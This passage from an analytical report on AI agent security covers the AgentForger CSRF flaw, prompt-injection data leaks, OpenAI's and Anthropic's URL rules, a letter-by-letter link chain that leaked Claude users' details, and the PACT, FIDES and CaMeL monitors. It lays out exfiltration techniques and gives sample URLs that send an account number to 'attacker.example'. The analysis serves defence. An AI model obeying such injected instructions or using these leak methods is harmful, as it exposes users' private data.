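Zenity reported the flaw on June 4, 2026 through Bugcrowd, a service that handles vulnerability reports. OpenAI accepted the report the next day and fixed the flaw on June 8. The fix removed the URL parameter, according to Zenity's July 23 press release, *One Click, One Attacker-Controlled Agentic Insider* (2026). The Hacker News' *ChatGPT AgentForger Flaw Could Deploy Rogue Workspace Agents via a Phishing Link* (2026) appears to confuse the builder with a separate drag-and-drop tool, whose planned retirement in November is not the fix.

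The evidence is a demonstration by Zenity, which has a commercial interest and is also the source for OpenAI's response. If OpenAI accepted the report as quickly as Zenity says, the central finding is more credible. However, Zenity gives no success rate for the link and writes that there is no evidence of anyone exploiting the flaw.

An administrator could have found the new agent, but only by looking for it, so SecurityWeek's *OpenAI Fixes ChatGPT Agent Flaw* goes too far in calling it invisible. OpenAI's product lists the agents each user has built, and Zenity acknowledges that a forged agent would appear in an inventory with its instructions and schedule. OpenAI's *Workspace agents security overview* (April 29, 2026) also describes logs of new agents, schedule changes and calls to connectors. Administrators still have reason to search after the fix, because removing the parameter would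 not by itself delete an agent that an earlier link had created.

### Cross-site request forgery

Zenity classifies AgentForger as cross-site request forgery (CSRF), in which an attacker makes a user's browser send a request the user did not intend. The attack depends on cookies, small values a website stores in the browser. The browser sends them back with later requests, and the site uses them to recognise a logged-in user.

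MDN's *Cross-site request forgery (CSRF)* gives the example of a malicious page with a hidden form for a bank transfer. When a customer logged in to the bank visits the page, its code submits the form. If the browser attaches the customer's cookie, the bank transfers the money. Filippo's *Cross-Site Request Forgery* describes this as a confused deputy attack. The browser has the customer's authority and uses it for the attacker, who never needs to see the bank's response.

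Websites have several standard defences:

- **The Origin header.** The browser names the site that made the request, and the bank refuses transfers requested from other sites. A newer header, `Sec-Fetch-Site`, gives the relationship between the two sites directly.
- **Unpredictable tokens.** The bank puts a random value in its own form and accepts a transfer only if the value comes back. The attacker's page cannot read or guess it.
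- **Cookie restrictions.** A cookie's `SameSite` setting controls whether the browser sends it with requests from other sites. `Strict` withholds it from all of them, while `Lax` allows it when the user follows an ordinary link.
- **A deliberate user action.** The bank asks the customer to confirm the transfer. OWASP's *Cross-Site Request Forgery Prevention Cheat Sheet* suggests considering user interaction for highly sensitive operations.

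Sites usually apply the first two defences only to requests that change data. They treat GET requests as read-only and let them through, since blocking them would break ordinary links.

### Which defences would have helped

Zenity's description implies that AgentForger involved two requests. The browser first opened the builder's page with a GET request. Code on that page then submitted the prompt from the URL. Security researchers call this variant client-side CSRF, because the genuine site's own code sends the unwanted request. The standard defences would probably have applied as follows:

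| Defence | When the victim opened the link | When the page submitted the prompt |
|---|---|---|
| Origin header | Browsers usually omit it when a user follows a link | It names OpenAI's site |
| `Sec-Fetch-Site` | It can identify a link from another site, but sites normally allow such links | It shows a request from the same site |
| Token in the page | A site does not normally require one to open a page | The genuine page can supply a valid one |
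| `SameSite=Lax` cookie | The browser sends it | The browser sends it |
| `SameSite=Strict` cookie | The browser withholds it if the link is on another site | The browser sends it |
| Deliberate user action | Opening the page is harmless without submission | The page waits for the user |

A `Strict` cookie might have interrupted the attack by making the victim appear logged out when the page first loaded. But if the page loaded anyway, its later requests would have included the cookie. The setting also inconveniences people who follow legitimate links, because they also appear logged out when they arrive.

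A token would have worked if OpenAI had required one in the link itself and tied it to the user's session. Only OpenAI's own pages could then have produced links that started the builder. But employees could no longer have sent each other links with ready-made prompts that ran automatically.

Requiring the user to press "send" is the best option, because it allows shared links but stops the automatic submission. It still relies on the user reading the prompt. Zenity's phishing email offered a time-saving agent template, and a victim who wanted it might well have sent a long prompt without reading it. Removing the parameter avoids this risk but makes prompts harder to share.

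Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* describes a similar, earlier weakness in OpenAI's chat page. When a user clicked a link, ChatGPT automatically submitted the text in the link's parameter as a prompt. One example told the chatbot to answer only "yes" from then on. With AgentForger, the same kind of automatic submission reached an agent that could publish other agents and change their approval settings.

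### A legitimate destination

The AgentForger link led to OpenAI's real website, a permitted destination, unlike the target of an SSRF attack. The seven-step check described for TicketOracle would have allowed the link because it used an `https` address on a public host. An allowlist would also have had to include that host for employees to use ChatGPT.

Nothing checked who had written the parameter. The usual CSRF defences check which site sent a request, which here was OpenAI's own, but not where the values inside it came from. The login identified only the person who opened the link, and the URL would have looked the same if that person had written it. A page that receives a prompt in a URL should therefore treat it as untrusted text. It can display the prompt but should not submit it as the user's own words.

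A destination check could have helped later, when the new agent emailed its results. OpenAI lets administrators limit the arguments of app actions across a workspace, and lets an agent's author set limits for that agent. An administrator's rule that agents may email only company addresses would probably have stopped those messages. A limit set by the author would have given little protection, because the attacker was in effect the author. Neither limit would have stopped the Teams message with the fake login page, because its recipients were the victim's real colleagues.

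### Approvals that passed to the new agent

The victim had authorised the connectors during earlier use of ChatGPT. The builder gave those connectors to a new agent that had different instructions, ran unattended and took orders from someone outside the company. The victim had no opportunity to judge this agent when they connected Outlook, so their earlier consent was not a good reason to give it access.

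OpenAI's *Managing app permissions in ChatGPT* describes an approval card on which a user can allow one action, allow low-risk actions or, in some cases, always allow an app's supported actions. OpenAI's *Beheerdersinstellingen beveiliging en naleving voor plugins en apps*, a help page for administrators, explains that these permissions cover ChatGPT conversations, while whoever builds a workspace agent sets separate controls for it. A cautious choice in chat therefore does not carry over to a new agent. This separation is useful when an employee sets the new agent's controls, but in AgentForger the attacker's prompt set them.

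The forged agent could reach only what the victim could reach, so limiting a new agent to its creator's access would not have solved the problem. ServiceNow's agents likewise stayed within the administrator's permissions when they leaked a ticket. AgentForger changed how closely anyone supervised that access. A rule for agents that create agents therefore has to cover approval settings, schedules and whose orders the new agent will follow, as well as its connectors.

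One way to enforce this is to give a new agent no connectors until the user approves them for that agent. Ordinary software, which a prompt cannot persuade to skip a step, could show a final screen before the agent goes live:

```
New agent: TASK Mail Operator
Can use: Outlook, Gmail, Slack, Teams, calendars
Sends email without asking: yes
Runs: every 5 minutes
Takes orders from: an address outside your company
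```

An employee who expected a productivity template would probably notice the last line, but the software may not be able to produce that line reliably because the agent's instructions are free text. The other lines come from settings, and unattended email on a five-minute schedule would itself be a reason to stop and look. Asking once before publication would also let employees approve agents that have a good reason to work unattended, without being prompted for every action.

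OpenAI already uses this kind of review for added restrictions. If a user describes a new limit on an app, the builder drafts a rule for the user to review before it takes effect. In Zenity's test, the builder removed an approval requirement without such a review, although loosening a control usually deserves more scrutiny than tightening one.

Zenity identifies a second cause of the flaw besides the automatic submission, which is the builder's ability to change approvals and schedules on instruction. Removing the URL parameter does not remove this ability. An attacker might still reach the builder through a document that an employee supplies as the description of a new agent, although Zenity does not report testing this route.

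## ChatGPT and Claude: rules on which links an agent may open

AgentForger used a link's parameters to bring an attacker's instructions into ChatGPT, and parameters can also carry private data out. OpenAI and Anthropic both limit which URLs their models may open automatically. OpenAI checks whether the exact address was already public, while Anthropic checks whether it has already appeared in certain parts of the conversation. Both rules stop the simplest leak, in which a model writes a secret into an address and opens it. A model can still leak information by choosing among permitted addresses, and Anthropic's rule protects less when the address comes from another agent.

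### Leaks that the answer does not reveal

*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) measured how often a web page could make an agent send private data to an attacker. The paper calls this leak "silent egress" because the data leaves in a web request while the answer the user sees looks normal.

The agent ran on qwen2.5:7b, a small open-weight model, with synthetic private data in its context. The user always asked for a summary of a page, and the agent's program fetched the page and added its text to the context, including the title and the description that search engines and chat apps show in previews. The attacker's instruction was in the title, the description, the body or the text of a link. In one example, the instruction was to verify the agent's connection by requesting a URL with the user's API key in the query.

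Lan and colleagues also varied whether the page arrived directly or through redirects, and whether the agent was told to send the data whole or in pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for a total of 480 runs. The agent contacted the attacker's server in 423 of them (88.1%). In 95% of the successful attacks, the final answer looked harmless, so checking only the answer would have missed them. In 120 runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted that server.

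To split the data, the agent cuts a key into four pieces and sends each in its own request with its position, so that the attacker can join them. A four-character piece looks like ordinary usage statistics, and a filter that searches each request for a complete key will miss it. The results for the 16 combinations add up as follows:

| Result | Data sent whole (240 runs) | Data sent in pieces (240 runs) |
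|---|---|---|
| The agent contacted the attacker's server | 238 | 185 |
| The first request contained private data | 232 | 63 |

Splitting made the attack harder to detect but less reliable, probably because the model had to keep track of the pieces. Lan and colleagues define a measure of how often the attacker got the whole secret but give no result for it. They also report finding private data in the first three requests less often (15.8%) than in the first request alone (26.3%), which is impossible under their definition. The fall in contacts from 238 to 185 is more trustworthy.

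Lan and colleagues acknowledge that their set-up favoured the attacker, since the secret was already in the context and the model had almost no security instructions. But they call their success rates a lower bound because the attacks were simple. That may hold for this agent, but not for commercial products with stronger defences. They also suspect that more capable models would be more vulnerable because such models follow instructions better, but GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4.6 refused every attack in the TicketOracle tests.

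### Defences in the prompt and on the network

Lan and colleagues then tested defences against one version of the attack, in which the instruction was in the page's body and the data was sent in one piece. They ran each defence 30 times.

| Defence | Agent tried to send data | Request reached the attacker |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Telling the model to ignore instructions in web content | 66.7% | 66.7% |
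| Tags that mark web content as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Both of these | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Allowlist of hosts | 100% | 0% |
| Filter for suspicious hosts and paths | 83.3% | 0% |
| Filter for words such as `api_key` and `password` | 23.3% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking values | 0% | 0% |

The allowlist gave the clearest result, because the agent tried to send the data every time and the allowlist blocked every attempt. But the test was easy, since Lan and colleagues chose an attacker's host that was obviously not on the list. The test of the filter for suspicious paths was also easy. The filter blocked the word `collect`, which appears in the paper's own attack URLs but which a real attacker would avoid.

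The last two filters are harder to judge. A filter that examines finished requests should not affect whether the model tries to send one, yet attempts fell from 100% to 23.3% and then to zero. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random-looking values when monitored, but they do not say that they told it about the monitoring. Something else may have differed between the runs.

There were no attempts, so the filter for random-looking values had nothing to block. For values longer than ten characters, it calculates the Shannon entropy, a measure of how varied the characters are, and blocks anything above 4 bits per character. The paper's example key, `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, scores about 3.85 and would pass. A four-character piece is too short for the filter to check.

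### Why trusted hosts can still leak

An allowlist works only if attackers cannot collect data through the hosts on it. Many well-known hosts let anyone open an account, and an attacker can then receive data there. Simon Willison, a software developer, describes several such cases on his weblog:

- The email app Superhuman allowed images from `docs.google.com`. Google Forms is on the same host and saves data sent in a GET request, so a planted instruction could send the contents of a user's emails to an attacker's form.
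- Anthropic's Claude Cowork allowed requests to Anthropic's own API. An attacker could supply a key to his own Anthropic account and have the agent upload the user's files there.
- Google's coding tool Antigravity allowed `webhook.site` by default, a service on which anyone can record incoming requests.
- Salesforce still trusted a domain whose registration had lapsed. Researchers registered it and received customer data from Salesforce's agent.

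OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives two further objections to lists of trusted sites. A trusted site may redirect the agent to an untrusted one. A strict list also produces many false alarms, because people use far more of the web than a few famous sites. People who see frequent warnings learn to click through them without thinking.

### OpenAI's index of public addresses

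OpenAI checks the whole URL instead of the host. A crawler explores the web much as a search engine does and builds an index of public URLs, without access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data. Before ChatGPT opens a URL automatically, OpenAI's software looks for that exact URL in the index. ChatGPT can open the URL if it is there; otherwise, the software either prompts the agent to try another website or shows the user a warning.

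This works because inserting a secret changes the URL. Suppose a page gets ChatGPT to open `https://attacker.example/log?account=48213`, where the number comes from the user's conversation. The crawler had no access to that conversation, so the URL is unlikely to be in the index. The same applies on a trusted host. Even if a public Google Form is in the index, the form's address with the user's emails added is not.

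The user sees the URL and a warning that the link is unverified and may include information from the conversation. An account number in plain text is easy to notice in the URL, but an encoded one would be much harder to recognise. A user who wants to finish the task quickly may also not check the URL carefully.

OpenAI promises only to prevent the agent from quietly leaking user data through the URL itself. It does not promise that the page is accurate or free of malicious instructions. An attacker can publish a false price list, wait for the crawler to find it, and have ChatGPT open it without a warning. OpenAI describes the rule as one layer of defence alongside training against prompt injection, monitoring and red-teaming.

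The rule also protects only the parts of a product that use it. Security researcher Johann Rehberger reported this type of leak to OpenAI in early 2023. According to his Embrace The Red blog post *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, OpenAI added a first check on URLs in December 2023 but left it out of its macOS and iOS apps. He also found ways around the check, and OpenAI strengthened it around August 2025. Rehberger considers the index a significant improvement but warns that some OpenAI developers may not know they need to use it.

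PromptArmor, a security firm, points out that messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram fetch links to show previews. If an agent writes a link containing private data in a message, the app may open it before anyone clicks. A rule in the agent's page-fetching tool would not prevent this, because the messaging app makes the request.

### Sending information by choosing a page

An agent can leak data even if every URL it opens passes a perfect check. Suppose an attacker's site has 32 ordinary pages, all in OpenAI's index, and an instruction on one of them tells the model which page to open for each possible value of a secret. The attacker can then see in the site's log which page the model opened. One choice among 32 pages conveys five bits of information, even though none of the URLs contains the secret.

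In general, a choice among *N* pages conveys log₂ *N* bits. A five-digit account number has 100,000 possible values, or about 16.6 bits, so four choices among 32 pages are enough to send it. The number of requests falls as the attacker adds pages:

| Permitted pages | Bits per choice | Requests needed for a five-digit number |
|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 | 17 |
| 10 | 3.3 | 5 |
| 32 | 5 | 4 |
| 1,000 | 10.0 | 2 |
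| 100,000 | 16.6 | 1 |

These counts assume the model follows the scheme without mistakes and the attacker receives the requests in order. In the last row, the attacker could publish a page for every possible account number. The URL ending in `?account=48213` would then be in the index, if the crawler recorded that many similar pages.

Rehberger described a simple version in 2023 that uses a separate URL for each letter and digit. It needs 36 pages, and he notes that any large blog probably has that many in the index already. According to Embrace The Red, OpenAI also acknowledges this weakness in its technical paper on the rule. The weakness remains because blocking it completely would require preventing the model from choosing which public pages to read.

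Rehberger suggests that OpenAI could make the attack harder by storing each response for a few minutes and reusing it, or by preventing an agent from opening the same URL twice in a session. Either would interfere with spelling a name such as "Anna", because the attacker's log would show the page for "n" only once. The attacker could get around this with a separate set of pages for each position in the word, which would take only 260 pages for ten positions with 26 letters each. Limiting the number of pages an agent opens from one site would restrict the total leak more directly, but would also hinder legitimate research.

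Even a small leak may matter. An attacker who wants to know whether a company plans to close a factory needs only one bit, which the agent can convey by either opening a page or not.

### Claude's rule on earlier appearances

Claude opens web pages through a tool called `web_fetch`, which runs on Anthropic's servers. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* warns developers about using it when Claude handles untrusted content together with sensitive data. To reduce the risk, Claude may not construct URLs for the tool itself. It can open only those that have already appeared in certain parts of the conversation. A newer edition of the documentation, Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, sets out which parts count:

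| Where the URL has appeared | Can `web_fetch` open it by default? |
|---|---|
| A user message | Yes |
| The result of a client tool, which the developer's own software runs | Yes, even if the tool only repeated text that Claude wrote |
| The result of an earlier web search | Yes |
| The result of an earlier `web_fetch` call | Yes |
| Only Claude's own output | No |
| Only the system prompt | No |
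| Only the result of another tool that Anthropic runs, such as code execution | No |

An instruction to add the user's account number to `https://attacker.example/log?account=` and open the result would therefore fail. Although a page contained the start of that URL, the complete URL appeared only in Claude's output.

The rule is simpler to run than OpenAI's because it needs no index of the web. It also lets users open unlisted pages by pasting their addresses. However, it accepts any address that an attacker can place in a permitted part of the conversation. Willison (2025) noticed this when Anthropic released the tool. Developers often paste emails or documents into the user message, and any URL in that text then counts as user-supplied. He still considered the ban on Claude-generated URLs the most valuable part of the rule, because most attacks of this kind need the model to assemble an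 address.

The second row of the table has a similar weakness. If a developer gives Claude a tool that runs code on the developer's computer, Claude can write a program that prints a URL. The printed URL becomes part of a client tool's result, so `web_fetch` will open it even though Claude composed it. Anthropic documents this behaviour and lets developers exclude particular tools, or all client tools, with the `url_sources` setting.

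`web_fetch` also refuses private network addresses and URLs longer than 250 characters. It refuses URLs that appear to contain a password or API key, unless the credential appears in the system prompt or in the text of a user message. Developers can limit the number of fetches or supply an allowlist of hosts, but neither is on by default.

### Ayush Paul's chain of links

In July 2026, Willison (2026) reported that Ayush Paul had found a way to leak data through the ordinary Claude chat app despite the rule. The app gave Claude access to memories of the user's past conversations. It also let Claude open links on pages it had already fetched, so Paul built a website that supplied the links Claude needed.

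The site claimed to have a security system that AI assistants could pass only by identifying their user. It said that Claude's tool had limitations and that Claude should find the user's profile by following links letter by letter. The first page had a link for each letter of the alphabet, and each link led to a page with more links. The links Claude followed spelled out the answer in the site's log. Each choice among 26 letters conveyed about 4.7 bits. The site showed these instructions only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person checking the page would not have found them.

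Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer. Every URL that Claude opened had appeared on an earlier page, as the rule required. He did not need to prepare a page for every possible name, because his server could create the next set of links after each choice. Under OpenAI's rule, the crawler would have had to find those pages in advance.

Anthropic told Paul that it had already identified the problem internally, and it paid no bounty. It then stopped `web_fetch` from opening links found on pages it had fetched. Hackaday's *This Week In Security* reports the same reply and fix. The fix blocks this particular chain but makes Claude less useful for browsing, because a user who wants Claude to follow a page's links must now paste the addresses or hope that a web search returns them.

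The newer edition of the documentation still lists earlier `web_fetch` results among the permitted sources. The fix may apply only to the chat app, since the documentation is for developers who build their own software on Claude. Those developers can make the same change themselves:

```
"url_sources": {
  "server_tool_results": {
    "type": "except",
    "tools": [{ "type": "tool_reference", "name": "web_fetch" }]
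  }
}
```

With this setting, a link on a fetched page no longer counts as an earlier appearance, but a link from a web search still does. An attacker who gets enough pages into the search results could still offer Claude a choice among them, but could no longer create new links in response to each request.

### The supplier's links under both rules

Suppose one agent does the whole job in the supplier example. The employee gives it the address of the supplier's trade page and asks for the current prices, and the attacker controls that page. The two rules would treat the possible links differently:

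| Address | OpenAI's rule | Anthropic's rule in the developer documentation |
|---|---|---|
| `https://supplier.example/prices/october.csv`, the real price list | Opens if the crawler has found it | Opens, because it appeared on a fetched page |
| `http://10.0.4.17/payroll/export` | Should not be in an index of public pages | Refused as a private address |
| `https://attacker.example/october.csv`, a false price list | Opens if the crawler has found it | Opens |
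| `https://attacker.example/log?account=48213`, with the number added by the model | Leads to a warning or another website | Refused |
| `https://supplier.example/orders/cancel?id=311` | Probably leads to a warning or another website | Opens |

OpenAI's rule may interrupt the legitimate task by warning the employee about the correct file. The crawler may not yet have found this month's price list, and it can never find one that only logged-in customers can see. With Anthropic's default settings, the price list opens, but so does the cancellation link, because both appeared on the same page. If a developer excludes links on fetched pages to prevent Paul's attack, the real price list won't open either.

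Neither rule replaces the destination check described for TicketOracle. Anthropic's tool blocks the payroll address because of a separate restriction, not because of where the address appeared. OpenAI's index probably excludes it, but a crawler might record a private address that is linked from a public page. A company that builds its own index is safest if it also runs the destination check.

### When another agent supplies the address

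The supplier example originally had three agents, and Anthropic's rule applies separately to each agent's conversation. Suppose the attacker's page offers a price list at `https://attacker.example/log?account=YOUR_ACCOUNT_NUMBER`. The reading agent returns this address unchanged. The planning agent knows the company's account number, fills it in and writes a task for the fetching agent:

```
{ "task": "Download the current price list",
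  "url": "https://attacker.example/log?account=48213" }
```

`web_fetch` would reject this address if the planning agent tried to open it, because the address exists only in that agent's own output. But the fetching agent has a separate conversation, and developers commonly deliver a task from another agent as a user message. The address has then "already appeared" in the fetching agent's conversation before that agent does anything, so `web_fetch` accepts it. The rule that stops an agent from opening an address it composed therefore doesn't stop it from opening one composed by another agent.

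The check for credentials fails in the same way. It treats a password as provided by the user if it appears in the text of a user message, but not if it appears in a tool result. A planning agent that passes on a URL containing an API key through a user message may therefore give the fetching agent permission to send the key. Delivering the task as a client tool's result would preserve the credential check, though the URL would still be acceptable by default.

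Developers could turn off these sources for the fetching agent, but then it would also refuse every legitimate address from the planning agent. A better solution is to check the address at the hand-off. Ordinary software would keep a list of the addresses that the employee wrote and those in the original text of web pages and search results. It would pass on an address only if it exactly matched one on the list. An address with the account number filled in would fail this test, as it would if one agent did the whole job. The software has to take the addresses from the original pages, not from the reading agent's report, because that agent's model could also have composed an address.

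This restores the rule but doesn't add the protections it lacked. The attacker's altered link to the payroll server did appear on the supplier's page, so it would pass and still need a destination check. Paul's chain of links would pass too. The rule suggested earlier for the supplier example lets an address from the supplier's page lead only to the supplier's host, which would keep the requests away from `attacker.example`. Someone who controlled the supplier's server could still read its log.

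OpenAI's index does not have this problem with hand-offs, because an address is either in it or not, whichever agent supplied it. Addresses that users enter may be an exception. Rehberger understands that ChatGPT treats these as safe for the rest of the session, and software that copied this exception would have to distinguish a user's message from another agent's. It would also have to decide whom to warn about an unknown address, since the employee may have left hours ago and a planning agent could approve an address it has just written.

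Data leaked through the choice of public pages is harder to detect when several agents make the requests. Suppose the planning agent has read the attacker's instructions and gives four fetching agents one page each, chosen from the same 32. Together, the four requests reveal the account number, but each fetching agent opens only one public page, which it did not choose. A limit on fetches per agent would not help, because each makes only one. Lan and colleagues recommend comparing requests to detect data sent in pieces. Here the comparison would have to cover all four agents, and a reviewer who saw only the requests would see four pages opened on the same site.

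## PACT: a separate rule for each argument

OpenAI's and Anthropic's rules cover a single argument, the address of a page to open. Most tool calls have several arguments, and outside content should be allowed to fill some of them but not others. *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security* (Fan, Li and colleagues, 2026) describes PACT, a monitor that applies a separate rule to each argument, based on what the argument does and where its value came from. PACT made no mistakes in tests that gave it perfect records of where each value came from. When it had to infer those records, it still stopped all or nearly all attacks, but the agents completed fewer ordinary tasks. PACT doesn't let an agent open a link it found on a page unless trusted software certifies the link first.

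### The recipient and the body

In Fan and colleagues' example, a user asks an agent to summarise `evil.com` and email the summary to `boss@company.com`. The page has to influence the email because the user wants it summarised. But an attacker who controls the page can add an instruction to send the summary elsewhere, and the agent may then put the attacker's address in the recipient field. In both cases, a simple log would show only that the agent read a page and then sent an email. *From Agent Traces to Trust* points out that such a log doesn't show whether the recipient, subject or body came from the page.

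PACT gives each tool a contract that lists its arguments and assigns each of them one of six roles:

| Role | Examples | Lowest trust accepted by default |
|---|---|---|
| Target: where the action is directed | Recipient, URL, file path, bank account | User |
| Command: what the tool executes | Shell command, query that changes a database | Trusted or user, depending on the tool |
| Credential: a secret that gives access | Password, API key | Trusted |
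| Content: text that the tool passes on | Email body, summary, report | External |
| Selector: which object the tool uses | Record number, filter | Depends on the tool |
| Control: how the tool behaves | Setting that allows overwriting | A cautious default |

The role depends on the tool as well as the argument's name. An argument called `query` is content in a web search but a command in a tool that changes a database.

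### Trust levels and the merge rule

The table uses PACT's four levels of trust. From highest to lowest, they are:

1. **Trusted:** constants that the agent's own software supplies.
2. **User:** values from the user's instructions.
3. **Tool output:** structured results from internal tools.
4. **External:** web pages, emails, retrieved files and outside services.

Every value carries a tag with its sources, its trust level and any obligations, which are conditions that must be met before a tool can use it. When an agent combines two values, PACT unites their sources and obligations and takes the lower trust level. For example, an agent might add an account number from the user's request to a URL from the attacker's page:

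```
"https://attacker.example/log?account="
    sources: web page          trust: external
"48213"
    sources: user              trust: user

"https://attacker.example/log?account=48213"
    sources: web page, user    trust: external
```

The user's number doesn't make the attacker's URL more trustworthy.

Before each tool call, the monitor checks every argument. The value must have enough trust for the argument's role, none of its sources may be on the argument's list of forbidden sources, and no obligation may remain open. If any argument fails, the monitor blocks the whole call. In the email example, PACT allows body text from an external source when the recipient came from the user, but blocks the call if the recipient came from the page. PACT doesn't have to recognise the page's instruction as malicious to do this.

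The list of sources matters when a value passes through several tools. An internal tool that reformats text from a web page may return it with the higher "tool output" level, but the page stays on the list. When Fan and colleagues switched off this tracking between steps, some attacks got through.

### Why one test for the whole call fails

Fan and colleagues compare PACT with what they call a flat monitor, which gives each tool one label. If the label is strict, the monitor blocks any call in which at least one argument falls below a fixed trust level. If the label is lax, it allows every call. They prove that no flat monitor can handle both of these calls to a messaging tool correctly:

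| Call | Source of the recipient | Source of the body | Correct decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user's task | User | Web page | Allow |
| The attack | Web page | Web page | Block |

Both calls contain an external argument, because the body in each comes from the page. A strict label therefore blocks the call the user wanted along with the attack, and a lax label allows both. PACT tells them apart because it requires user-level trust for the recipient but accepts external text in the body.

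The proof applies only to monitors that check whether any argument is untrusted. A policy for the whole call can also distinguish the two cases if it checks each argument's label. Accounts of FIDES and CaMeL, the two defences that Fan and colleagues compare with PACT, show that both can make this distinction, although Fan and colleagues say they cannot.

### FIDES and CaMeL

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a Microsoft system that labels data by whether it is trustworthy and who may read it. If a model reads an untrusted email, everything it writes afterwards becomes untrusted too, which may prevent it from sending any message. FIDES avoids this by storing untrusted results in variables and showing the model only their names. The model can put a variable's name in a later tool call, and ordinary software fills in the value.

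When a task requires reading the hidden text, FIDES gives the text to an isolated model that has no tools. FIDES can restrict that model's answer to "yes" or "no", which limits the attacker's influence to one bit. A policy might allow actions based on such an answer but reject free text from the same source.

Costa and colleagues give an example of a policy that requires a trusted recipient but accepts an untrusted message, as in PACT's email example. The policies they tested were less precise. The main one checked whether the decision to make a call came from a trusted context, and ignored the labels on the arguments. Another blocked outgoing messages containing untrusted links, which could leak data.

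FIDES tracks data that goes directly into a tool call, but not information that an agent reveals through its choice of calls, so it would not fully protect against leaks like Paul's chain of links.

*CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes how CaMeL, from Google DeepMind, separates planning from reading. A planning model receives the user's request and writes a short program for the task before the agent reads any untrusted content. When the program needs information from an email or web page, a quarantined model without tools extracts it. An interpreter runs the program and records each value's sources and permitted readers. Before every tool call, a policy uses the arguments and these records to allow or deny the call.

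Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, gives an example in which the user asks an agent to find Bob's address in the last email and send him a reminder. In simplified form, the planning model writes:

```
email = get_last_email()
address = ask_quarantined_model("Find Bob's address", email)
send_email(recipient=address,
           subject="Meeting tomorrow",
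           body="Remember our meeting tomorrow")
```

An instruction hidden in the email can't add a step to this program, but it can make the quarantined model return the attacker's address. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which models such agents in a small programming language, describes a similar case in which the injected text cannot change the subject or body, and the recipient keeps its untrusted label. CaMeL also checks individual arguments. In Willison's example, it allows `send_email` only if the recipient is trusted, and can otherwise ask the user.

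PACT adds a standard set of roles with default rules, whereas CaMeL depends on people to write and maintain suitable policies, which Willison considers a serious burden. PACT also lets the model change its plan after each result, because every check relies only on what has happened so far.

### The supplier's link as a target

In the one-agent version of the supplier example, the employee supplies only the address of the trade page. Under PACT, the download tool's `url` argument is a target, so its value needs at least user-level trust:

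| URL | Source | Trust | PACT's decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| `https://supplier.example/trade` | Employee | User | Allow |
| `https://supplier.example/prices/october.csv`, the real price list | Supplier's page | External | Refuse |
| `http://10.0.4.17/payroll/export` | Supplier's page | External | Refuse |
| `https://attacker.example/log?account=48213` | Supplier's page and employee | External | Refuse |

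PACT stops the attacks but also the employee's task, as any rule based on origin alone would. Its solution is certification. A trusted procedure can examine a value that failed a check and issue a certificate. In simplified form, a certificate for the real price list might be:

```
{ "failed_check": "minimum trust",
  "procedure": "supplier_link_check",
  "roles": ["target"],
  "maximum_trust": "user" }
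```

The certificate resolves only the named check, and the value keeps its original sources. Each argument's contract lists the procedures it accepts. The company could therefore accept this procedure for downloads but not for uploads, so that a certified link can't be used as an upload destination.

Fan and colleagues do not specify how a procedure should examine a link. Costa and colleagues suggest that an agent looking for a password-reset link could accept only links from trusted senders, and perhaps infer the valid domains from the user's request. For the supplier's price list, a procedure could require that:

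1. the exact URL appears in the original text of a page that the employee named;
2. the URL and that page have the same host;
3. the URL passes the full destination check described for TicketOracle;
4. its path begins with `/prices/` and it has no query.

The first three tests, which combine checks suggested earlier, exclude both harmful links in the table. The fourth excludes the supplier's order-cancellation link, but somebody has to know how the supplier organises its website and update the rule when that changes. All four tests would still accept a false price list if the attacker replaced the file on the supplier's server.

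A company could instead certify any URL in an index of public addresses like OpenAI's. This would need no rule for each supplier, but it would let through a false price list on a public site.

The user could also confirm the link, but as with OpenAI's warnings and Aider's confirmation, people may approve it without recognising the danger.

### The cost for agents that follow links

A research agent may follow dozens of links from search results and other pages, and PACT treats all of them as external. Without certification, the agent could open only addresses from the user or its own trusted software. Certifying every public link would let it browse freely but leave little protection beyond the destination check. The company has to choose how much of the web to certify, and the right choice will differ between tasks.

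This limitation also affects other targets. *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), a benchmark for agents that handle untrusted data, includes a task in which the user asks the agent to invite Dora to Slack and says her email address is on her website. In another task, the user asks the agent to pay a bill stored in a file, which presumably names the account to pay. In both cases the user wants outside content to determine the target, so PACT would refuse the calls, even with correct roles and provenance, unless a procedure certified the values.

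The user's instruction could justify an exception. It names Dora's website, so a procedure could accept an email address only from that site. *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes a later design that derives permissions from the user's authenticated request alone, so text from a page cannot expand them. That would suit Dora's case well, but a broad request such as "research this company" gives little basis for deciding which links to permit.

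### Seventeen scenarios with perfect provenance

Fan and colleagues first tested PACT with correct contracts and perfect information about every value's origin. The 17 scenarios involved email, messaging, files, code, outside services and calendars. According to the paper, each contained both a legitimate action and an attack, but the published percentages fit nine legitimate cases and eight attacks:

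| Defence | Legitimate cases allowed, out of 9 | Attacks blocked, out of 8 |
|---|---|---|
| None | 9 | 0 |
| FIDES, reimplemented | 6 | 3 |
| CaMeL, reimplemented | 3 | 8 |
| PACT | 9 | 8 |

The comparison provides little evidence about FIDES and CaMeL themselves, because Fan and colleagues wrote simplified versions of both and treated them as defences that judge whole calls. A CaMeL policy that checked only the recipient would distinguish the two cases in the email example, as PACT does.

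PACT's perfect score is also less informative than it looks. The test defined an attack as untrusted content filling a sensitive argument, which is what PACT forbids. With correct labels, the monitor should block every attack unless the software has a bug. None of the legitimate cases can have required an uncertified external target, because PACT would have refused it. The test shows that the rule works on the problem it was designed for, but it leaves out tasks like Dora's invitation.

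PACT passed 180 further tests with controlled labels. These tests included 30 attacks that Fan and colleagues generated after finalizing the contracts, so the researchers could not have adjusted the contracts to those attacks. The tests also included 75 longer tasks, in which the agent replanned over 5, 10 or 20 steps.

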